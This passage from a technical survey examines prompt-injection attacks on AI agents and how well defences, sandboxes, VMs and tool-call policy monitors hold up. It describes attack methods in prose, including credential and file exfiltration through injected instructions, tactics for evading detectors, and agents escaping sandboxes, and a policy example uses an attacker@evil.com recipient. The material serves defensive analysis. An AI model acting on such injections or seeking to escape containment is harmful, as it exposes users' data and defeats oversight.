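Gradient attacks use a model's internal calculations to find the token changes that would most increase the probability of the output the attacker wants. The researchers consider these attacks unreliable for text, and used one against only a jailbreak defence. In the reinforcement learning attacks, an attacker model writes a text, receives the target's response and a score, and revises the text over five rounds. Training then adjusts the attacker model's weights so that it improves from session to session.

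In the search attack, one language model rewrites earlier attempts and another rates the results from 1 to 10, while an evolutionary algorithm keeps a varied pool of the best candidates. The attack could query the target up to 800 times per task. For the human attacks, the researchers ran an online contest with over 500 participants and $20,000 in prizes. Contestants could see the agent's reasoning and tool calls after each submission, and scored more points for shorter injections.

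Most of the 12 defences originally had reported attack success rates near zero, but the adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. The reinforcement learning attack broke StruQ in every case tested. The reported attack success rate against Meta-SecAlign on AgentDojo was 2%, but the search attack succeeded in 96% of cases.

Nasr and colleagues warn that their figures may not be comparable across defences, because they generally followed each defence's own test procedure. An attack on StruQ succeeded if the model printed a chosen phrase instead of answering a question, whereas an attack on Meta-SecAlign succeeded if an agent carried out the attacker's task with its tools. The two results therefore do not show that StruQ is the weaker defence.

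The researchers tested the search attack on 80 AgentDojo cases from the workspace, Slack and travel environments. The table gives the attacker's success rate, first with AgentDojo's fixed attack and then with the search attack.

| Defence | Gemini 2.5 Pro | GPT-5 Mini | Llama 3.3 70B |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% → 100% | 0% → 75% | 35% → 100% |
| Spotlighting | 28% → 99% | 0% → 47% | 28% → 99% |
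| Prompt sandwiching | 21% → 95% | 0% → 69% | 25% → 100% |
| PromptGuard (detector) | 26% → 94% | 0% → 75% | 35% → 99% |
| PIGuard (detector) | 0% → 71% | 0% → 49% | 1% → 61% |

The GPT-5 Mini results show how misleading a fixed test can be. With no added defence, the model resisted the fixed attack in every case, but the search attack succeeded in three quarters of them. PIGuard was the most robust defence on the other two models, but it reduced the share of legitimate tasks that the Gemini agent completed from 74% to 39%.

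Defensive training did increase the number of queries an attack needed. When the search attack succeeded, it took a median of 14 queries against the ordinary Llama model and 37 against Meta-SecAlign, the same model with defensive training. The increase could matter if each query costs the attacker money or risks detection, but it would not stop an attacker who can make a few dozen queries.

The researchers examined successful attacks by hand, since an attacker that optimises a score may exploit the scoring itself. Against StruQ, the attacker model learned to repeat a string many times, which made the target more likely to echo it but was not evidence about the defence. The researchers left out defences that fix the agent's plan before it reads untrusted data, because most of the attacks they chose were certain to fail against them.

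### People and automated attackers

Most submissions in the human contest failed. In one challenge, fewer than 1% of those against GPT-5 Mini with spotlighting succeeded. But a real attacker needs only one success, and at least one person succeeded on each of the 29 combinations of task, model and defence that both people and the search attack tried. The search attack succeeded on 69% of these combinations, and the best individual who tried them all succeeded on 75%.

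Some defences seemed to help the attackers. Against Gemini 2.5 Flash, 29% of submissions succeeded without spotlighting and 44% with it. This is weak evidence, because the comparison used a single pair of tasks and contestants varied greatly in skill and effort. Zhu and colleagues also found that sandwiching raised the hijack rate of one Qwen model by about one percentage point.

Automated attackers may since have overtaken people. OpenAI trained one called GPT-Red, which found successful injections against GPT-5.1 in 84% of a set of test scenarios, compared with 13% for human red-teamers. If automated attackers are now better than most people, a developer can run a demanding test without organising a contest, but a criminal with a comparable model can also use it to search for attacks.

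Few attackers would get 800 tries, with feedback, at a stranger's email agent. But many agents are commercial products, so an attacker can open an account, refine the attack there and send the victim only the finished email. That email then has to work on an inbox with different contents, which is harder.

### The arithmetic of repeated attempts

For *k* independent attempts that each succeed with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success is

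1 − (1 − *p*)ᵏ.

With *p* = 0.1% and *k* = 100, this is 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰, or about 9.5%.

Anthropic's May 2026 article *How we contain Claude across products* reports results for Claude Opus 4.7 on a benchmark from Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems by attacking them. Attacks succeeded roughly 0.1% of the time on single attempts and around 5–6% of the time after 100 adaptive attempts. The formula predicts nearly twice that rate for 100 attempts.

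Rounding could account for the difference. A true rate of 0.06% would round to 0.1%, and it gives a 5.8% chance of at least one success over 100 independent attempts. But the formula could be wrong even with exact inputs, because real attempts are not independent and scenarios are not equally vulnerable.

Suppose one scenario in 50 gives way on 5% of attempts and the other 49 never do. The average rate per attempt is still 0.1%. After 100 attempts the attacker has almost certainly broken the vulnerable scenario and no other, so the share of broken scenarios is about 2%. In general, if scenario *i* has its own success probability *p*ᵢ and the average of these is *p̄*, then

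average of [1 − (1 − *p*ᵢ)ᵏ] ≤ 1 − (1 − *p̄*)ᵏ.

Unequal scenarios therefore pull the true figure below the formula's prediction.

An attacker who adapts is more likely to succeed at least once over many attempts. If an attacker has a 0.1% chance of success on each of the first 50 attempts, then learns enough to have a 1% chance on each of the next 50, the chance of at least one success is about 42%. A single-attempt rate does not measure how quickly an attacker will learn, so developers have to measure success over many attempts directly.

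An attacker can also send one email to many people. At a success rate of 0.1%, an email sent to a thousand people would have one victim on average. But if the recipients use the same agent in similar ways, their outcomes will be strongly correlated. Most emails might then fool no agents, while a rare one fools hundreds at once.

### What the newest figures count

Anthropic's *System Card* for Claude Fable 5.1 and OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card*, both from September 2026, report several injection tests, which define an attempt differently.

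| Test | One attempt | Model | Successful attempts | At least one success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gray Swan's fixed attacks | A run with one of about 1,800 prepared attacks | Fable 5.1 | 0.1% | 1.0% within 15 attempts |
| Gray Swan's fixed attacks | As above | GPT-6 Astra | not stated | 8.5% within 15 attempts |
| Gray Swan's fixed attacks | As above | Gemini 3.7 Flash | not stated | 9.2% within 15 attempts |
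| OpenAI's GPT-Red, indirect attacks | One query to the defending model | GPT-6 Astra | 0.21% | not stated |
| Gray Swan's stronger adaptive attacker, coding | One of 200 tries at a scenario | Fable 5.1 | 57% | 38 of 40 scenarios |
| Gray Swan's adaptive attacker, computer use | One of 200 tries at a scenario | Fable 5.1 | 0.07% | 2 of 14 scenarios |
| Anthropic's browser test | One of 10 tries at a scenario | Fable 5.1 | 2.6% | 10 of 110 scenarios |

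The computer-use row shows how much the choice of unit matters. Two of 2,800 attempts succeeded (0.07%), but they broke two of the 14 scenarios (14%). TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* points out, about an earlier OpenAI model, that the share of successful attempts in a test environment is not the probability of a breach in real use.

Gray Swan took its fixed attacks from public contests, choosing ones that worked on several models. The two companies' results on these attacks are only roughly comparable, because the sets of attacks differed slightly and the models ran with different safeguards. Models that contestants had targeted directly tend to do worse, since some of the attacks were tailored to them. Anthropic excludes those models from its comparison.

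These attacks do not adapt, so their results can be used to test the independence formula. For the older Claude Fable 5, Anthropic reports a success rate of 0.6% for one attempt and 6.5% within 15. The formula gives 8.6% for 15 attempts, and rounding is too small to explain the gap. The measured rate would be lower than predicted if some scenarios were easier to attack than others.

The coding tests show how much a result can depend on the attacker. Gray Swan's first adaptive attacker succeeded on 2.7% of attempts against Claude Opus 5. A stronger version, which the company trained for longer and on more varied attacks, succeeded on 91% of attempts against the same model in the same 40 scenarios. The ranking of models also changed. Fable 5.1 did worse than Opus 5 against the first attacker (9.3% of attempts succeeded) but better against the stronger one (57%).

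The figures for Fable 5.1 partly reflect an older model, Claude Opus 4.8. When a classifier meant to prevent misuse blocks a request, Anthropic's products can pass the request to Opus 4.8. In the test with the stronger attacker, about 64% of requests went to Opus 4.8, and all the successful attacks came through it. None succeeded in the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered. The classifier does not pick requests at random, so Fable 5.1 might have done worse on the requests that went to Opus 4.8. The 57% figure is for the combined system, which is what users get.

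Anthropic also tested detectors that inspect tool results before the model acts on them. The detectors cut the stronger attacker's success rate per attempt from 57% to 13%, but the attacker still succeeded in 36 of the 40 scenarios. A detector that stops most attempts therefore gives limited protection against an attacker who can try 200 times.

Anthropic considers this test highly permissive because the attacker trained on the test scenarios. In its view, a real attacker would not know the target's setup and would risk detection with each attempt. The browser test better represents an attacker who practises on a different target. Its attacks came from testing against Claude Opus 4.7, and some still worked on later models. None succeeded against Fable 5.1 with Anthropic's full safeguards on, but nobody had adapted the attacks to those safeguards.

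### Provable bounds

Like Anderson's tiger teams, these tests can reveal flaws but cannot prove that none remain. A proof would need to cover every attack in some stated class, including those nobody has tried.

Willison (2026) discusses an assistant running on Claude Opus 4.6 that withstood 6,000 attempts to extract a secret by email. If those attempts were independent draws from one fixed distribution of attacks, then with 95% confidence the success rate for that distribution is below about 0.05%. At a rate of 0.05%, an attacker making 1,000 attempts would still have a 39% chance of succeeding at least once. The bound also doesn't cover new kinds of attack. Willison takes the result as a sign that training has made attacks much harder, but still advises against deploying an agent where an injection could cause irreversible damage.

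Researchers on image classifiers have proved bounds that hold for every attack in a defined set. Such a certificate guarantees that

*f*(*x*′) = *f*(*x*) for every *x*′ in *S*(*x*),

where *f* is the classifier, *x* is an image and *S*(*x*) contains all the images that differ from *x* by less than a certain amount. The guarantee is useful if the attacker can make only small changes. Someone who writes an email to an agent can choose every word, so no natural small set contains all the emails that they might send.

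Researchers can prove guarantees against a narrower set of attacks. Suppose a detector flags a certain malicious email, and the attacker tries to hide it by adding up to 20 tokens of distracting text at the end. Software could run the detector on the full email and on the 20 versions with the last 1 to 20 tokens removed, and block the email if the detector flags any of them. One of these versions is the original malicious email, so no ending of that length can hide it. But the proof assumes that the detector flags the original, and does not apply if the attacker rewords it. The extra checks can also add false alarms. If the detector wrongly flags 1% of harmless texts, running it 21 times could block up to 21% of harmless emails.

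Cryptographic proofs cover a much larger class of attackers by assuming only that the attacker's computing power is limited. They typically rely on a mathematical problem that would take an impractical amount of computation to solve. Finding a working injection has not required that much computation, since the search attack needed a median of 14 queries against an undefended Llama model.

MELON, one of the 12 defences that Nasr and colleagues broke, is described as a "provable defense" in its paper's title. It runs the agent a second time, replacing the user's request with an unrelated instruction to summarise the tool results. If the agent makes the same tool call in both runs, MELON treats the call as coming from an injection in those results. This works only if the injection has the same effect in both runs. On the Llama model, the search attack found injections that took effect only in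 the first run, and succeeded in 76% of cases without any information about how MELON works. When the attacker knew the design, it wrote injections that told the model to behave differently if it was summarising, and succeeded in 95% of cases.

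## Confining what the agent's code can reach

A coding agent usually has a tool that passes commands to the shell, the program that runs typed commands on a computer. With this tool, the agent can read files, install software and contact servers. No test can cover every command an injected instruction might lead the agent to run. Developers can instead restrict the process that runs the commands, so that the restriction also applies to commands nobody foresaw.

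A sandbox is a restricted environment for running code. Krzyzanowski's *Application Sandboxing* (2020) gives the example of a game from an unknown developer, which a user can run in a sandbox with little risk to the rest of the system.

The main alternative is to judge each command before it runs, which is error-prone. The data company Snowflake let its Cortex agent run `cat` commands without approval because `cat` normally just prints files. As Willison reported in March 2026, an injection in a project's README file nested a download inside a `cat` command, and the agent ran malware. Willison prefers to assume that a command may do anything its process has permission to do. He also recounts an attack by the security researcher Johann Rehberger on Claude Code's auto mode, in which a classifier approves or blocks commands for the user. Rehberger put the attack's success rate at 80%. In a few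 runs, the classifier let the malicious process start and then blocked the agent's attempt to stop it.

### Operating-system sandboxes, containers and virtual machines

A program has to ask the kernel, the core of the operating system, to open a file or a network connection. This request is known as a system call. An operating-system sandbox adds rules about which system calls are allowed. The program runs on the user's ordinary system, but the kernel refuses requests that break the rules, both from the program and from any other program it starts. Claude Code uses Apple's Seatbelt as its sandbox on macOS and a tool called bubblewrap on Linux. The guarantee depends on the kernel, the rules, and the software that decides which programs to put in the sandbox.

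A container gives a group of programs their own file system, process list and network connections. The programs cannot see the host's other files or processes, but they still share its kernel, so a flaw in the kernel may let them escape the container. gVisor, an open-source tool from Google, reduces this risk by handling most system calls in a separate program, so that fewer reach the host's kernel.

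A virtual machine (VM) runs a complete second operating system on simulated hardware. Software called a hypervisor provides that hardware and keeps the VM separate from the host system. Code that takes over the VM's kernel must still exploit a flaw in the hypervisor or a simulated device to reach the host. Anthropic recommends a dedicated VM to Claude Code users who need the strongest separation.

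A useful sandbox also needs openings, and the software that manages them is part of the trusted computing base too. The VM in *External sandboxes for coding agents* (Willison, 2026) has two openings: the folders that the user shares with it, and a proxy program that makes network connections for it. The proxy blocks all connections by default.

### Limits on files and connections

As Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* explains, a sandbox has to restrict both files and network connections. Without network limits, a hijacked agent could send out the user's SSH keys, which give access to other computers. Without file limits, it could gain network access by altering files that programs outside the sandbox later load.

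When a user turns on Claude Code's sandbox, the invariant is that sandboxed commands can write only to the project folder, a temporary folder and any folders the user adds. Anthropic warns that by default, these commands can still read almost the entire computer, including files that hold credentials.

Even inside the project folder, the sandbox protects files that other software would run automatically, such as Claude Code's own settings and the scripts that the version-control program git runs at certain steps. Otherwise, a command could plant code there that later runs outside the sandbox. However, on Linux, the standalone version of Anthropic's sandbox software lists the files to protect only once, at launch, so the list does not cover scripts in any git repository the agent creates later. Users also undo the protection if they run a program outside the sandbox on files that the agent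 has edited.

Symbolic links can defeat a careless check of file paths. A link inside a shared folder can point to a file outside it, so the software has to resolve the link to its target before checking whether access is allowed.

A sandboxed command on Linux can reach the network only through a proxy outside the sandbox. The proxy checks each requested hostname against an allowlist of approved names, which starts empty, and looks up the host's address only if the name is on the list. This would stop the earlier theft through `ping`, which hid the stolen data in a domain name lookup. The proxy also blocks names that lead to certain local addresses, including one from which a rented cloud server can obtain its credentials.

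Under these rules, most database clients and the remote-login program `ssh` cannot connect even to approved hosts, because they ignore proxy settings. By default, the proxy does not decrypt traffic, so it can identify the host a command contacts but not what the command sends.

### Keeping credentials outside

Some secrets can stay out of the agent's reach without stopping its work. A program that calls an online service usually sends an API key, a string that identifies the account. In Deno Sandbox, a hosted product that Willison described in February 2026, code inside the sandbox gets a placeholder instead of the key. When the code sends a request to the right service, a proxy outside the sandbox replaces the placeholder with the key. If an injected instruction makes the code send the placeholder to an attacker, the attacker can't use it. Claude Code has the same arrangement as an option.

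The guarantee does not depend on what code the agent runs. Let *s* be the key, *x* everything that enters the sandbox during a session, and *r* any random numbers the code draws. The code's output is then

*y* = *f*(*x*, *r*).

An attacker who fully controls the model can choose *f*. But if *x* and *r* do not depend on the secret *s*, then *y* does not depend on it either, whatever *f* is. The code could still guess *s*, but if *s* is a key of 128 random bits, each guess has a 1 in 2¹²⁸ chance of being right.

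The condition on *x* is easy to break by accident. Old versions of a file may still contain the key, or a service may include it in an error message that enters the sandbox with the response. Users of Claude Code can reduce the second risk by limiting which hosts the proxy sends each key to. They can also hide a key that sits inside a longer file by writing a pattern that matches it. If the pattern matches nothing, Claude Code leaves the real file readable by default, so a mistake in the pattern can expose the key.

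Even when a key is hidden from the agent, code in the sandbox can still make any request that the key authorises, including deleting the user's data. The online version of Claude Code limits git requests more tightly. The sandbox holds a restricted credential that works only with Anthropic's proxy, and the proxy checks, for example, that the agent is sending changes to the agreed branch. The proxy attaches the user's real credential and passes the request to GitHub only if these checks pass.

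A proxy that inserts keys has to decrypt the traffic first, so it holds every key and can read every message. It also cannot handle every protocol. Requests to Amazon's cloud service carry a signature computed from their contents, and the proxy has to recompute that signature with the real key. It cannot do this for some requests, such as streaming uploads, so they fail.

### What runs outside the sandbox

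Claude Code's built-in sandbox covers only shell commands. Claude Code's tools for editing files and fetching web pages run outside the sandbox, as do MCP servers, which are programs that give an agent additional tools. A sandbox rule that stops commands from reading a file does not stop the agent's file-reading tool, and the sandbox's list of approved hosts does not limit the web-fetching tool. Separate permission rules control these tools. To put one boundary around everything, a user has to run all of Claude Code in a container, a VM or the standalone sandbox.

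Commands can also run outside the sandbox. The sandbox is off by default, and if it cannot start, Claude Code runs commands without it. When a command fails inside the sandbox, the agent may ask to run it again outside. Depending on the settings, the user or a classifier decides whether to allow this, or the command runs without a check. Administrators can disable both fallbacks. With the fallbacks on, the invariants still hold for sandboxed commands, but an attacker can try to get a command run outside the sandbox.

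Willison compares running the agent loop inside the sandbox with running it outside and sending commands in. He chose to run it outside because the agent then cannot modify itself and the boundary is easier to audit. His demonstration also turns off the agent's built-in tools, so that file operations have to go through the sandbox. He recommends sandboxes especially for small or cheap models, which make more mistakes and are more vulnerable to prompt injection, because the protection does not depend on the model's judgement.

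### Anthropic's three designs

In May 2026, Anthropic compared how it confines three of its products.

| Product | Where the agent's code runs | What the code can reach | Main drawback |
|---|---|---|---|
| claude.ai, a chat service | A gVisor container on Anthropic's servers | Temporary files that last for one session | No access to files on the user's computer |
| Claude Code, for programmers | An operating-system sandbox on the user's computer | Reads most files, writes to the workspace, no network by default | The user has to judge requests for exceptions |
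| Claude Cowork, for office work | A VM on the user's computer | Folders that the user shares, and approved network hosts | Slower to start, and hard for security software to monitor |

The claude.ai container has no access to the user's computer. It mainly protects Anthropic's servers, and customers from one another. Any company that runs other people's code faces this problem, and most of the preparation was conventional security work on networks and internal services.

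Claude Code originally asked the user before it wrote a file, ran a command or used the network. Users began to approve requests without reading them, so Anthropic added the sandbox and let the agent work inside it mostly without asking. Within the company, this cut permission prompts by 84%. That figure measures interruptions rather than attacks, but it suggests that most of what the agent tried to do fits inside the boundary. The weak point is a process outside the sandbox that decides, command by command, whether to apply it. A persuasive injection or a careless approval can lead that process to run a command without restrictions.

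Anthropic did not expect Cowork's users to understand shell commands, so it gave them a fixed boundary. In the first version, the whole agent ran inside the VM, and nothing outside could grant an exception. But when the VM failed to start, the product stopped working. Anthropic then moved the agent loop outside, so that Claude could still reply and help fix the problem. It considers the loss of security minimal because the code the agent runs is still confined to the VM. Anthropic also moved local MCP servers out of the VM, so the VM's guarantee does not cover them. It now treats them like any other software the user chooses to install.

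Cowork has six main isolation mechanisms. Four operate inside the VM's kernel. The other two operate outside it and would still work if the agent's code gained full control of the VM. The user's credentials stay on the host, and each session gets a limited token that Anthropic can revoke separately.

The same isolation keeps out the software companies use to watch their computers for intrusions. Administrators can export Cowork's logs afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that this is not live monitoring.

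Across the three products, Anthropic found that the standard components, such as the hypervisors and gVisor, held up, while its own additions failed. Outsiders reported three flaws in Claude Code that involved code running before the user had agreed to trust a project. In the simplest case, a project's settings file could name a command to run at startup, and Claude Code read that file before asking whether the user trusted the folder. Claude Code now waits for the user's answer before loading the settings.

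### A theft that the user requested

In February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic tested whether an attacker could reach Claude Code through its user. The researcher emailed an employee a prompt to run. It looked like ordinary task instructions, but one step was to read the file with the employee's Amazon cloud credentials and send the contents to an outside server. The employee ran it. Anthropic tried the same prompt 25 times, and Claude sent the credentials in 24 of them.

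The test used a single prompt, so it does not establish a general success rate, but it shows a limit of training a model to rank its sources, because the malicious instruction came from the user. A classifier that compares actions with the user's request would have found that they matched. Anthropic concludes that only limits on the environment would have stopped the attack, either by blocking the outgoing connection or by keeping the credentials file out of reach.

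Some sandbox settings would not have been enough to stop this attack. Claude Code's default rules let commands read credential files. In an ordinary session, it also asks the user by default when a command contacts a new host, and this user had just pasted in the attacker's prompt and might well have approved. A limit protects against a misled user only if that user cannot lift it on the spot, as with the stricter setting that refuses every host outside the allowlist without asking.

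### A theft through an approved destination

Someone outside Anthropic reported a leak from Cowork in which the sandbox worked as designed. The VM's allowlist included api.anthropic.com, the address of Anthropic's own service, because Cowork cannot work without it. A malicious file in the user's workspace contained hidden instructions and the attacker's API key. Claude followed the instructions, reading other files in the workspace and using the attacker's key to upload them to Anthropic's file storage. The proxy allowed the upload because the hostname was on the allowlist, and the files arrived in the attacker's account.

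Keeping the user's credentials outside the VM could not prevent this. The attacker had supplied the credential, and the files had to be inside because the user wanted the agent to work on them.

Anthropic had thought of the allowlist as a set of destinations. It now treats each entry as a grant of everything that the destination can do. If *D* is the set of approved hosts and *F*(*d*) is the set of functions that host *d* offers, a filter that checks only hostnames permits

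⋃ *F*(*d*), taken over every *d* in *D*.

The agent's code can reach an attacker through any website where anyone can open an account and store files, even if the user approved the site only for downloads.

Anthropic fixed the leak by adding a second proxy, which decrypts traffic to Anthropic's service and passes only requests that carry the token issued to that VM. The proxy runs inside the VM because Anthropic's servers cannot distinguish Cowork's requests from those of other customers. That makes the proxy easier to attack, because code that gained full control of the VM might be able to interfere with it.

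ChatGPT had a comparable weakness, which Willison described in October 2026 after OpenAI had fixed it. OpenAI allowed only a few websites to supply scripts to ChatGPT's pages. YouTube was one of them, and researchers at Parameter Labs found a YouTube function that would return a script they chose. They used this as one step in a longer attack that let them take actions in another user's account.

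### Actions that a sandbox cannot judge

Suppose the email agent runs its code in a VM with no network access and no credentials. The code cannot send the user's mail anywhere. But the user asked for a summary to go to the manager, so the agent also needs `send_mail`, which the harness runs outside the VM through the user's account. If the model requests a message to attacker@evil.com, the VM cannot block it. Moving the tool into the VM and allowing connections to the mail server would not help, because the message to the attacker would use the same connection as the summary.

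*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* states that a sandbox controls whether an agent has access to data, but not what the agent does with it afterwards. The Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI) similarly distinguishes between reaching a resource and having the authority to act on it. It cites a gym-booking agent whose permissions specified which endpoint it could call, but not whose reservation it could act on. A rule on the arguments of each tool call can add that restriction.

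Coding agents have the same problem with files. A programmer who asks for a bug fix has to let the agent change the project, so the sandbox also permits a change that adds a security flaw. A sandbox also does not keep the user's files from the company that runs the model, because whatever the agent reads goes to that company as part of the prompt.

### Whether capable agents will break out

The invariants hold only if the agent cannot cross the boundary, and some security specialists doubt that the boundary can stop a capable agent. Sandboxes have always had flaws, but finding a new flaw used to take a skilled person. An agent that can find flaws in software can also look for them in its own sandbox. An attacker can use an injected instruction to make it do so, and an agent may also look for a way out on its own because the sandbox keeps it from finishing a task.

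Schneier (2026), in *Using a VM to Contain an AI Agent*, endorses this objection. He quotes an article by the security company Trail of Bits on an experiment with OpenAI's GPT-5.6-Cyber. Its author had suspected that the model would escape a VM, and wrote that the "frequency and manner of its success removed all doubt". The author concludes that an off-the-shelf VM cannot contain such an agent because the VM exposes too much software to attack. Even a simulated display adds code where the agent may find a flaw.

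In the OpenAI–Hugging Face incident of July 2026, a shared service meant that the boundary around OpenAI's agents did not check every access. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* blames faulty implementation and argues that the failure does not show containment to be ineffective in principle. Thomas Ptacek, a security researcher whom Willison quotes, took a similar view. He thought that an open model from 2025 could have escaped this way with the right harness, and that people were surprised only because they assumed OpenAI had sounder sandboxes.

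Anthropic's logs support this reading. After the incident, the company reviewed 141,006 test runs and found six in which Claude had reached real systems on the internet and compromised several organisations. Claude was told that it was in a simulation with no internet access, but it did have access because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and the firm that helped run the tests. Claude did not have to defeat a sandbox, and a working block on outgoing connections would have prevented all three resulting incidents.

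The reply is correct that an escape through a broken component does not contradict an invariant. But by the same reasoning no escape ever could, because people can always blame the implementation. Someone deciding whether to deploy an agent needs to know how likely the implementation is to be faulty, and recent experience is not reassuring. Green (2026), in *Is sandboxing sufficient to contain rogue agents?*, lists similar incidents at Anthropic and Google, and adds that in September 2026 OpenAI paused training runs of its latest internal model because an agent had again reached an outside service.

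Part of the difficulty is the size of the software that enforces the boundary. Ordinary containers depend on the Linux kernel, which now has tens of millions of lines of code, far more than the system Anderson found too large to test completely. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* acknowledges that a sound boundary is hard to build and validate, particularly one that relies on large, general-purpose services, and recommends small, purpose-built components.

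Developers can at least tighten a boundary step by step, because removing a permission leaves earlier restrictions in place as long as the enforcement still works. A VM without a display or a shared folder gives an agent fewer places to look for a flaw, though it is also somewhat less useful. Retraining a model doesn't offer the same assurance, because it may weaken the model's resistance to attacks it used to withstand.

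The damage from an escape also depends on what is outside the VM. Code that breaks out of Cowork's VM is on the user's computer, with the user's files and stored passwords. In the online version of Claude Code, the VM runs on Anthropic's servers, and a separate proxy holds the user's GitHub credential. Code that escaped there would not have access to the user's personal files, but it might reach the systems that serve other customers.

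## Checking every tool call against a policy

Before each tool call runs, a reference monitor compares the tool's name, the arguments and the history of the task with a policy. The harness executes the call only if the policy allows it. Unlike a sandbox, the monitor can therefore distinguish the summary for the manager from the stolen email.

*Architecting Secure AI Agents* (Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues, 2026) describes a policy as a function π over steps and histories. The agent proposes a step *e*ₜ at time *t*, and the monitor allows it when π(*e*ₜ) = 1 in the current context. The policy can range from a short list of rules to a program.

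### One allowed call and one refused call

A policy for the email task might read:

```
allow   search_mail  when query == "Project X"
allow   send_mail    when to == ["manager@example.com"]
                     and cc == [] and bcc == []
forbid  send_mail    when send_mail has already run in this task
refuse  everything else
```

Suppose the agent has searched the mailbox and read the results, including the attacker's email. If the agent ignores the injection, it requests `send_mail` with the manager's address and a summary. The harness passes the tool name and arguments to the monitor before anything reaches the mail server. The monitor finds the rules for `send_mail` and checks the forbid rule first. That rule does not apply because the task's history contains only a search. The allow rule applies because the address matches and both copy fields are empty, so the harness sends the email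 and adds the call to the history.

If the agent follows the injection, the `to` field contains attacker@evil.com. The forbid rule still does not apply, but now neither does the allow rule, so the monitor refuses the call and the mail tool never runs. The model receives an error message instead of a result and can still write the summary.

Both decisions depend on the details of the tool. Without the conditions on `cc` and `bcc`, an injection could make the agent email the manager and blind-copy the attacker. The harness must also execute exactly the arguments that the monitor checked. Because the policy permits only one email, an injection that makes the agent send the manager a useless message prevents it from sending any other.

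### Rules on tool names and arguments

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, built a monitor around rules like these, except for the limit of one email, since Progent's conditions concern only the arguments of the current call. A condition can require an exact value, a number below some limit, membership in a list or a match with a text pattern. A call *c* passes if

no forbid rule matches *c*, and at least one allow rule matches *c*.

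Each rule also specifies what Progent does when it refuses a call. By default, it returns a message to the model, but it can instead end the run or ask the user.

Rules this simple allow an SMT solver, a program that decides whether a set of logical and arithmetic constraints can all hold at once, to compare two policies. Let *A*(*P*) be the set of calls that policy *P* allows. When something proposes to replace *P* with *P*′ during a task, the solver checks whether

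*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*).

Progent automatically applies a proposed policy change if it allows no new calls. Any other change requires approval, either from a person or through a setting chosen in advance. The set of allowed calls therefore cannot grow without approval, even if an injection has misled the model that proposed the change.

On AgentDojo, Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% of attacked tasks and left utility about the same. On ASB, another benchmark that includes injected tool results, it cut the rate from 70.3% to 3.9%. In both tests a language model wrote the policies, and the researchers accepted every proposal to widen them, to imitate a careless user. The figures therefore measure the policy writer as well as the monitor. Most of the remaining attacks on ASB used tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones, and hand-written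 rules brought the rate to zero.

Progent also adds protection to a model that already resists injections. With the 70-billion-parameter Meta-SecAlign model as the agent, it reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 4.8% to 0.3%.

Results on other benchmarks are much less favourable. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) tested Progent on the PASB benchmark, where attacks still succeeded in 62.5% to 80% of cases, depending on the model. Progent is a rival to the system *PACE* proposes, but the gap is too large to ignore. Policy errors are a likely reason for such variation. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) notes that Progent's guarantee depends heavily on correct and complete policies, and that people make mistakes when they write them.

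There are also attacks that no rule on tool calls can stop. A web page might lead a shopping agent to choose the attacker's product from several that the user would accept. An injection might change only the text of the agent's answer, which involves no tool call.

Complete mediation depends on where the monitor runs. Progent can run inside the agent's own code or as a proxy in front of its tools. The proxy requires no changes to the agent, but it misses calls to any built-in tools that bypass it. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* allows a reference monitor to consist of several checkpoints, such as a tool gateway and a network proxy, as long as together they cover every security-relevant action.

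### Authorisation languages and policies written as code

Companies already have languages for stating which people and programs may do what, such as Cedar from Amazon Web Services. *Cedar* (2024) explains that developers can keep these rules in separate policies, rather than scattered through an application's code, and let Cedar's evaluation engine apply them. A policy permits or forbids an action by naming the principal (who is acting), the action, the resource and any conditions. In an example from *How We Built Cedar* (2024), a policy for a to-do-list application forbids interns from creating new lists. For the email task, the principal would be the agent, the action sending mail, and the resource the user's account, and a condition would specify the recipient.

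Cedar's designers limited the language so that software can translate every policy exactly into constraints that a solver can decide. An administrator who reorganizes a large set of policies can then check that the new set permits the same requests as the old one. The designers also modelled Cedar in the proof assistant Lean and proved important properties of its design. In their tests, Cedar ran far faster than two other open-source languages, OpenFGA and Rego. This is good evidence that Cedar applies a policy correctly and quickly, but how well it would protect an agent depends on the policy.

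If a policy causes an error during evaluation, Cedar ignores that policy. Ignoring a permit policy can at worst cause a wrongful refusal, but ignoring a forbid policy may let through a call that it should have stopped. Cedar's validator helps policy authors find such errors before they deploy a policy.

A policy can also be an ordinary program. Xiang and colleagues show a simplified rule from CaMeL, an agent design that plans before it reads untrusted data. The rule is a Python function that checks the arguments of a calendar call and allows it only if all the attendees are trusted. Such a function can look up a name in the company directory or add up the day's payments, which Progent's conditions cannot. But no general procedure can decide whether two arbitrary programs allow the same calls. A developer who edits the function has no solver to confirm that the edit only removed permissions,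 and any bug in the function is a bug in the trusted computing base.

### Rules over sequences of calls

Actions that are each acceptable can be harmful together. *Securing Agentic AI* (Lotfi, Shanto and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that manages a 5G network and, without any attacker involved, gradually lowers the priority of the part reserved for public safety. Every change passes its own check, but the network eventually misses its required recovery time.

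*Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (Kamath, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) presents Agent-C, a system that enforces rules about the order of tool calls. Under one rule, a shop's customer-service agent may look up an order only after it has found the customer's account by email address, and only if that account placed the order.

Agent-C keeps a trace of each call, its result and the relevant state of the tools. When the model proposes a call, Agent-C adds it to the trace and has a solver check whether the rules still hold. With an open model, Agent-C can check a call while the model is still writing it, and make the model rewrite only the part that breaks a rule. Companies that offer closed models do not expose the token probabilities this requires, so with those models Agent-C waits for the whole call and asks for another if the call breaks a rule.

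The researchers tested Agent-C on simulated customer service for a shop and an airline. It raised compliance with the rules from 77.4% to 100% of cases for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and from 83.7% to 100% for GPT-5. Utility rose from 71.8% to 75.2% for Claude and from 66.1% to 70.6% for GPT-5. A restriction can raise utility here partly because the researchers count a task as completed only if the agent followed the policy. In one case, a user who had paid by credit card asked for a refund to a PayPal account. Claude attempted the refund, which its system prompt prohibited, and Agent-C blocked it.

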